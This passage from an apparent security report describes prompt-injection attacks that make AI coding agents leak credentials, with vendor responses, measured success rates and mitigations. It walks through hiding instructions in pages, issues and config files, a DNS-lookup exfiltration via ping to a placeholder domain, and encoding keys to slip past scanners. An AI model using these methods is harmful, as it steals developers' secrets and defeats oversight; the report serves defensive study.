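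Companies don't usually pay for reports of known flaws, and the page gave users accurate information, but Google applied the exclusion broadly. AI Incident Database's *Indirect Prompt Injection in AI IDEs* (2025) includes a researcher's finding that Antigravity's system prompt told the model to strictly follow messages inside a certain tag and not to mention them to the user. Antigravity didn't remove that tag from web pages, so an attacker could put it in a page and the model would treat the text inside as an instruction from Google's own software. The attack worked every time with the tag and less often without it.

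Google could have fixed this flaw by removing the tag from outside text. Instead, it replied within a day that the flaw was "Intended Behavior" and linked to a known issue about leaks through images. The researcher published five days later. PromptArmor didn't report its attack privately, reasoning that Google already knew about the risk. Treating these leaks as a known issue may have saved Google some duplicate reports, but it also meant that working attacks became public before any fix.

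Pillar Security found a different kind of flaw in Antigravity, which let attackers run commands through its file-search tool even in Secure Mode. Secure Mode, the strictest setting, isolates terminal commands and restricts their network access, but the search tool ran before those restrictions applied. According to CyberScoop's *Vuln in Google's Antigravity AI agent manager could escape sandbox*, Pillar reported the flaw on 6 January 2026, and Google patched it on 28 February and paid a bounty. Engineers can fix a flaw like this by checking the tool's input, but to stop the image leak, Google would have to restrict a feature that users see.

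The image leak still worked in June 2026. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (2026) hid instructions in the title of an otherwise empty web page. The instructions were disguised as the log of a failed software build, with steps for repairing it. The agent listed the computer's environment variables, took an API key and displayed an image whose address contained the key. The user had asked the agent to do what the page said, which favored the attacker.

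In this test, Antigravity asked the user to approve generating a "visual debug token" but did not show the command or the address, and the user agreed. Rehberger had warned Cognition about this weakness in 2025, when he recommended that approvals take place outside the chat.

It is unclear whether Google has changed how Antigravity loads images since June. Secure Mode restricts what terminal commands can do on the network, but the chat window loads images separately. Antigravity now also has a setting that stops the agent from accessing files outside the open workspace. In a forum post titled *"Agent Non-Workspace File Access" needed for the agent to work with project files*, one user complained that the agent once worked around this setting. Even if the setting works as intended, it doesn't protect a `.env` file, which is normally inside the workspace.

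## Claude Code, Amazon Q and the GitHub workflow agents

Some vendors fixed credential leaks quickly. Anthropic fixed one in its coding agent, Claude Code, eleven days after Rehberger reported it in 2025. Amazon fixed the same flaw in Amazon Q Developer before he published it that August. In both products, the agent could leak the secret through a network command that it could run without asking for approval.

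### How a name lookup carries a secret

Claude Code asks for approval before running most shell commands, but not those on a built-in allow-list. Rehberger found this list in the program's code and asked Claude which entries an attacker could misuse. As he recounts in Embrace The Red's *Claude Code*, the model identified four network diagnostic tools, including `ping`, which checks whether another computer responds.

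Suppose an attacker owns the domain `collector.example`, and the developer's `.env` file contains the invented key `demo-key-7730`.

1. The developer asks Claude Code to review a source file that contains planted instructions.
2. Claude Code reads the key and tells `ping` to contact a computer called `demo-key-7730.collector.example`.
3. `ping` needs a numerical address for that name, so the developer's computer asks its usual domain-name server, which often belongs to an employer or internet provider.
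4. That server doesn't know the address, so it asks the server responsible for `collector.example`, which the attacker runs.
5. The attacker's server logs the name it received, including the key.

The leak works even if no computer has the name being looked up. A firewall that blocks connections to the attacker's server doesn't prevent it, because the developer's computer contacts only its usual domain-name server. A name can hold about 250 characters, enough for most API keys but not for a large file.

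Claude refused Rehberger's direct requests for the key, so he disguised what the command would read. Claude also refused to contact domains known for security testing, but it accepted an ordinary domain of his. A test that used only those testing domains would have made Claude Code look safer than it was.

Rehberger reported the flaw on 26 May 2025 and suggested taking the four commands off the allow-list. Anthropic reported a fix on 6 June, in version 1.0.4, which most users received through automatic updates. OSV's public record, *GHSA-x5gv-jw7f-j6xj* (2025), lists the flaw as CVE-2025-55284, with a severity of 7.1 out of 10, and gives an overly broad allow-list as the cause. This repair was easier than the one Rehberger wanted from Cognition, because asking for approval before a rarely used command seldom interrupts the user.

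Blocking DNS lookups completely is harder. Zenity Labs' *It's Always DNS in Claude's Sandbox* describes an isolated environment where Claude runs code. All web traffic had to pass through a proxy, which correctly blocked outside connections. But DNS lookups went out before the proxy applied its rules, so they could still carry data.

### Amazon Q and Cursor

Amazon Q Developer sorted shell commands into categories such as "readonly" and "destructive", and ran the read-only ones without approval. According to Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer*, the read-only category included `ping`, which leaves the developer's files unchanged but sends a hostname over the network. It also included `find`, a file-search command that can start other programs, so an attacker could plant text that led the agent to run any command through it.

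Amazon began requiring approval for `find` on 17 July 2025 and for the lookup commands on 29 July. AWS's advisory, *Amazon Q Developer and Kiro* (2025), followed on 7 October. It says that the lookup leak requires the developer to accept a suggestion containing the commands, and that it could expose "metadata". This makes the flaw sound milder than the equivalent one in Claude Code, where Rehberger took an API key without the developer's approval.

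Amazon Q had another credential leak in 2026. A configuration file in a downloaded project could steal the developer's Amazon cloud credentials through an MCP server. The Next Web's *A single config file in a cloned repository* reports that Amazon now requires approval before an MCP server starts and restricts which environment variables it can access. The restriction still helps if a developer approves a malicious server by mistake.

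Cursor, another code editor with an agent, had the same image leak as Devin and Windsurf, but through its diagrams. It draws them from text in a notation called Mermaid, and a diagram could include an image from an outside address. Cursor fixed this flaw, CVE-2025-54132, in version 1.3. A vendor that blocks outside images in ordinary replies also has to block them in every other format its chat window can display.

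### Permitted domains that strangers can use

Like Superhuman AI's image policy and Antigravity's browser allow-list, the web version of OpenAI's Codex permitted a domain where attackers could receive data. Its preset list covered domains programmers commonly need for software packages, but Rehberger found that it included a cloud provider's domain, where anyone can rent a server and get an address. Codex would therefore connect to a server that an attacker had rented there.

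Claude Code had a similar problem with Hugging Face, a site where anyone can publish AI models. Vulners' *CVE-2026-54316 Claude Code* explains that the whole site was approved in advance for the agent's web-page tool, including pages that an attacker controls. The flaw affected versions from 0.2.54 until 2.1.163.

A vendor can reduce this risk by allowing particular pages instead of whole domains. This works for a package site that the agent only downloads from, but not for GitHub, where many agents have to publish results on pages that strangers can read.

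### Comment and Control

GitHub Actions runs automated jobs, called workflows, in response to events in a project. For example, a workflow can start an AI agent whenever someone files an issue or opens a pull request (a proposed code change). The job runs on a temporary machine, and maintainers can give it secrets, such as the model's API key.

In April 2026 the security researcher Aonan Guan published an attack on three such agents, developed with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University. Guan called it "Comment and Control", a play on the "command and control" servers that criminals use to direct malware. The attacker writes instructions on GitHub, the agent reads them, and the stolen credentials come back through GitHub as well.

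Guan (2026), in *Comment And Control Prompt Injection Credential Theft*, describes how each agent leaked:

- Claude Code Security Review, Anthropic's tool for checking pull requests, inserted the title of the pull request directly into the model's prompt. The tool started Claude with no limits on its tools and with all of the job's environment variables. A malicious title made Claude collect the credentials, and the tool posted them in a comment as a "security finding".
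- Google's Gemini CLI Action included issue titles, descriptions and comments in its prompt. After a series of planted comments, it posted its own API key in public.
- GitHub Copilot Agent works on issues that a maintainer assigns to it. The attacker hid the instructions in an HTML comment, a kind of note that GitHub doesn't display but the model receives. The maintainer saw only a harmless request.

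The first two attacks could start without any action by a maintainer. However, GitHub by default withholds secrets from workflows triggered by an outsider's pull request, so the pull request attack works only where maintainers have overridden that default. Some override it so that the agent can review outside contributions automatically.

Copilot was the best protected of the three. GitHub removed sensitive variables from the agent's shell, scanned its changes for known kinds of credentials, and put the machine behind a firewall that allowed only listed domains. Guan got past the first protection because other programs on the same machine still held the variables, and the shell could inspect those programs. The agent then encoded what it found so the scanner didn't recognise it, and added the encoded text to a file in a pull request. Guan could download the file and decode the text.

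The firewall had to allow this last step because submitting code to GitHub is Copilot's job. It could identify GitHub as the destination but could not detect the credentials in the file. Blocking unknown domains stops an agent from contacting an attacker's own server, but this attack sent the credentials through GitHub instead.

### What the three vendors did

Anthropic rated the flaw critical, at 9.4 out of 10, and paid $100. It told Guan that the tool "is not designed to be hardened against prompt injection", added security advice to the documentation, and blocked the command that had revealed the credentials. Guan objected that other commands can reveal the same information. He recommended allowing only the few tools a reviewer needs.

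Google paid $1,337. Guan told SecurityWeek (*Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection*) that Google had added instructions to the system prompt to resist such attacks, but had left the agent's tools unchanged. The new instructions might stop the particular comments he used in his attack, but they still rely on the model to follow them.

GitHub first closed the report, saying the problem was already known and it couldn't reproduce the leak. Guan replied with parts of Copilot's code that showed GitHub had built a filter to prevent this kind of leak. GitHub then reopened the report and paid $500. It called the leak a "previously identified architectural limitation" and said it was looking for ways to restrict access further.

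The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties, then kept quiet* reports that none of the three published an advisory or assigned a CVE number, the standard public identifier for a flaw. Microsoft is named because it owns GitHub. Projects using older versions of these tools therefore had no official notice to update. Anthropic had assigned a CVE number to the lookup leak the year before.

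Microsoft soon found another leak in one of Anthropic's workflow tools, Claude Code Action. The action can run shell commands in a sandbox that doesn't contain the job's secrets, and it does so automatically when outsiders can trigger the agent. But the agent's file-reading tool ran outside the sandbox and could open a system file that lists the secrets. Microsoft planted text that described the task as a compliance review and had the model leave off the start of the key so that GitHub's scanner wouldn't recognise the rest.

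Microsoft reported this on 29 April 2026, and Anthropic blocked access to such files on 5 May. In August the security firm Novee presented further critical flaws in coding agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI. Underhill (2026) reports in *Black Hat 2026* that Novee found the flaws in the vendors' own GitHub projects, with default settings, and that a stranger could attack them by opening a single issue.

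### How often the attacks work

In *Your AI, My Shell*, Liu, Zhao and colleagues (2025) measured how often attacks succeed against two code editors, Cursor and GitHub Copilot in VS Code. Their test system, AIShellJack, has 314 planted instructions, each describing something an attacker might do on a Linux computer. They hid these in rule files, which developers download to tell an agent how to write code, and asked the agent to reorganise a project according to the rules. Both editors could run any command without approval.

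When Cursor chose the model itself, it carried out 67% to 84% of the attacks, depending on the project. The average was 68% for instructions aimed at finding credentials and 56% for those aimed at sending data out, though only nine of the 314 instructions were of the second kind.

How often the attacks succeeded depended on the editor as well as the model. On one project, Cursor with Claude 4 Sonnet carried out 69% of the attacks, and Copilot with the same model carried out 52%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, Cursor carried out 77% and Copilot 41%.

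These rates are probably higher than an ordinary user would have faced at the time. The editors had permission to run anything, and they treat rule files as guidance to follow, so the planted text carried more authority than a web page would. Liu and colleagues also counted an attack as successful if the agent ran only part of the intended command, though a manual check found that about 90% of the successes were complete. Wording also made a large difference. In a smaller test of 20 instructions, one version with less forceful framing succeeded once and another never succeeded.

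Newer models resist prompt injection much better, but how the injected text reaches them still matters. In *GitInject*, Isbarov, Suleymanov and colleagues (2026) ran attacks in real GitHub workflows on temporary projects. They compared instructions in a pull request's description with instructions in a configuration file, such as `CLAUDE.md`, added by the pull request. The workflow fetched the proposed code before the review, so the agent loaded the attacker's file as if the project's owner had written it.

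The configuration files worked on seven of the nine models tested, including Gemini 3.1 Pro, but not on Claude Opus 4.7 or GPT-5.4. In one comparison, three Gemini models never leaked their API key when the instruction was in the description, but leaked it in all five runs when the instruction was in the file. Five runs are too few to rule out occasional failures, but the contrast shows that a vendor can undo a model's resistance by labelling a stranger's text as trusted.

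Nakibly and Babo (2026), in *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, searched about 143 million GitHub issues, pull requests and comments for hidden text addressed to AI agents. They found 43 attacks, 19 of which tried to steal secrets. Several attackers had clearly studied their targets. One issue, filed in July 2026 on Google's Gemini CLI project, addressed the agent that looks for duplicate reports and correctly named the tool it uses to run commands. Some of the 43 attacks may be the work of security researchers, and the search missed any attack written in visible text.

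Nakibly and Babo then gave the 43 texts to five recent models with simulated tools. Three Claude models (Haiku 5.5, Sonnet 5.5 and Opus 5.5) and the larger of two GPT-5.6 models followed none of the instructions in them. The smaller one, GPT-5.6 Luna, followed the instructions in eight, including four of the 19 designed to extract secrets. Small, cheap models are a natural choice for sorting every new issue, so the model most susceptible to injection may well read the most text from strangers.

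The stronger models sometimes stopped the attack but left the user's task undone. Opus, for example, returned no answer to 22 of the 43 items.

The results also depend on how hard the attacker tries. The test in which all 720 injections failed used Claude Code's auto mode, in which a model decides which actions need approval. It ran 72 prepared scenarios ten times each, according to Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary*. Rehberger's later attacks on the same mode worked in three of five, three of five and four of five runs, so his 80% success rate comes from only five attempts.

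### Limiting the damage

Several defences work even when the model follows the attacker's instructions. Isbarov and colleagues tested some of them against nine pull request attacks and checked whether five ordinary reviews still worked.

| Change to the workflow | Attacks that still worked (of 9) | Credentials still stolen | Ordinary reviews that still worked (of 5) |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 9 | GitHub token, Gemini API key | 5 |
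| Don't leave the GitHub token on disk after fetching the code | 6 | Gemini API key | 5 |
| Remove tools such as the shell | 5 | None | 4 |
| Delete Markdown files, including agent instructions, from the fetched code | 3 | GitHub token | 4 |
| All three changes | 2 | None | 4 |
| Run the agent only for trusted authors | 0 | None | 4 |

Keeping the token off the disk takes one line in the workflow file and had no drawbacks in these tests. Combining the three changes stopped every credential theft. The two attacks that still worked made the agent approve bad code or waste money on the model. Restricting the agent to trusted authors stopped every attack, but it also denies automatic review to outside contributors, and many projects set up the agent to review their code.

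A stolen token is less useful to an attacker if it has few permissions and expires quickly. GitHub creates a new `GITHUB_TOKEN` for each job and revokes it when the job ends. Maintainers can also restrict its permissions, so an agent that labels issues can read issues and add labels but not change code. These restrictions matter because an attacker can still use the token while the job runs. Model API keys usually keep working until someone revokes them. Microsoft recommends a separate key for each workflow, with alerts for unusual use. Devin supports short-lived tokens for cloud services.

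Keeping the secret off the agent's machine is safer still. A separate program can hold the key and add it to the agent's requests before forwarding them to the right service. Planted text could still make the agent misuse that service during the session, but the agent would have no key to leak. Devin's option to remove the GitHub command-line token from its machine comes close to this design.

Anthropic's and GitHub's agents instead left the secrets on the machine and hid them from the shell. Guan and Microsoft got around this by reaching the secrets through another program or tool. Anthropic has since blocked the route that Microsoft found, but each new tool could open another route.

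Rules for outgoing traffic vary between products. Local Codex blocks network access by default, Devin's allow-list is optional, and Copilot Agent has a firewall that permits GitHub. If an agent reads strangers' text on GitHub, the rules also have to cover what it can publish there. A project could have the agent choose a label from a fixed list and let ordinary software apply it, so that the agent has almost no way to include a stolen key in what gets published. Nakibly and Babo say the agent's choice of label should never be enough to pass a security check, since an attacker may have influenced it.
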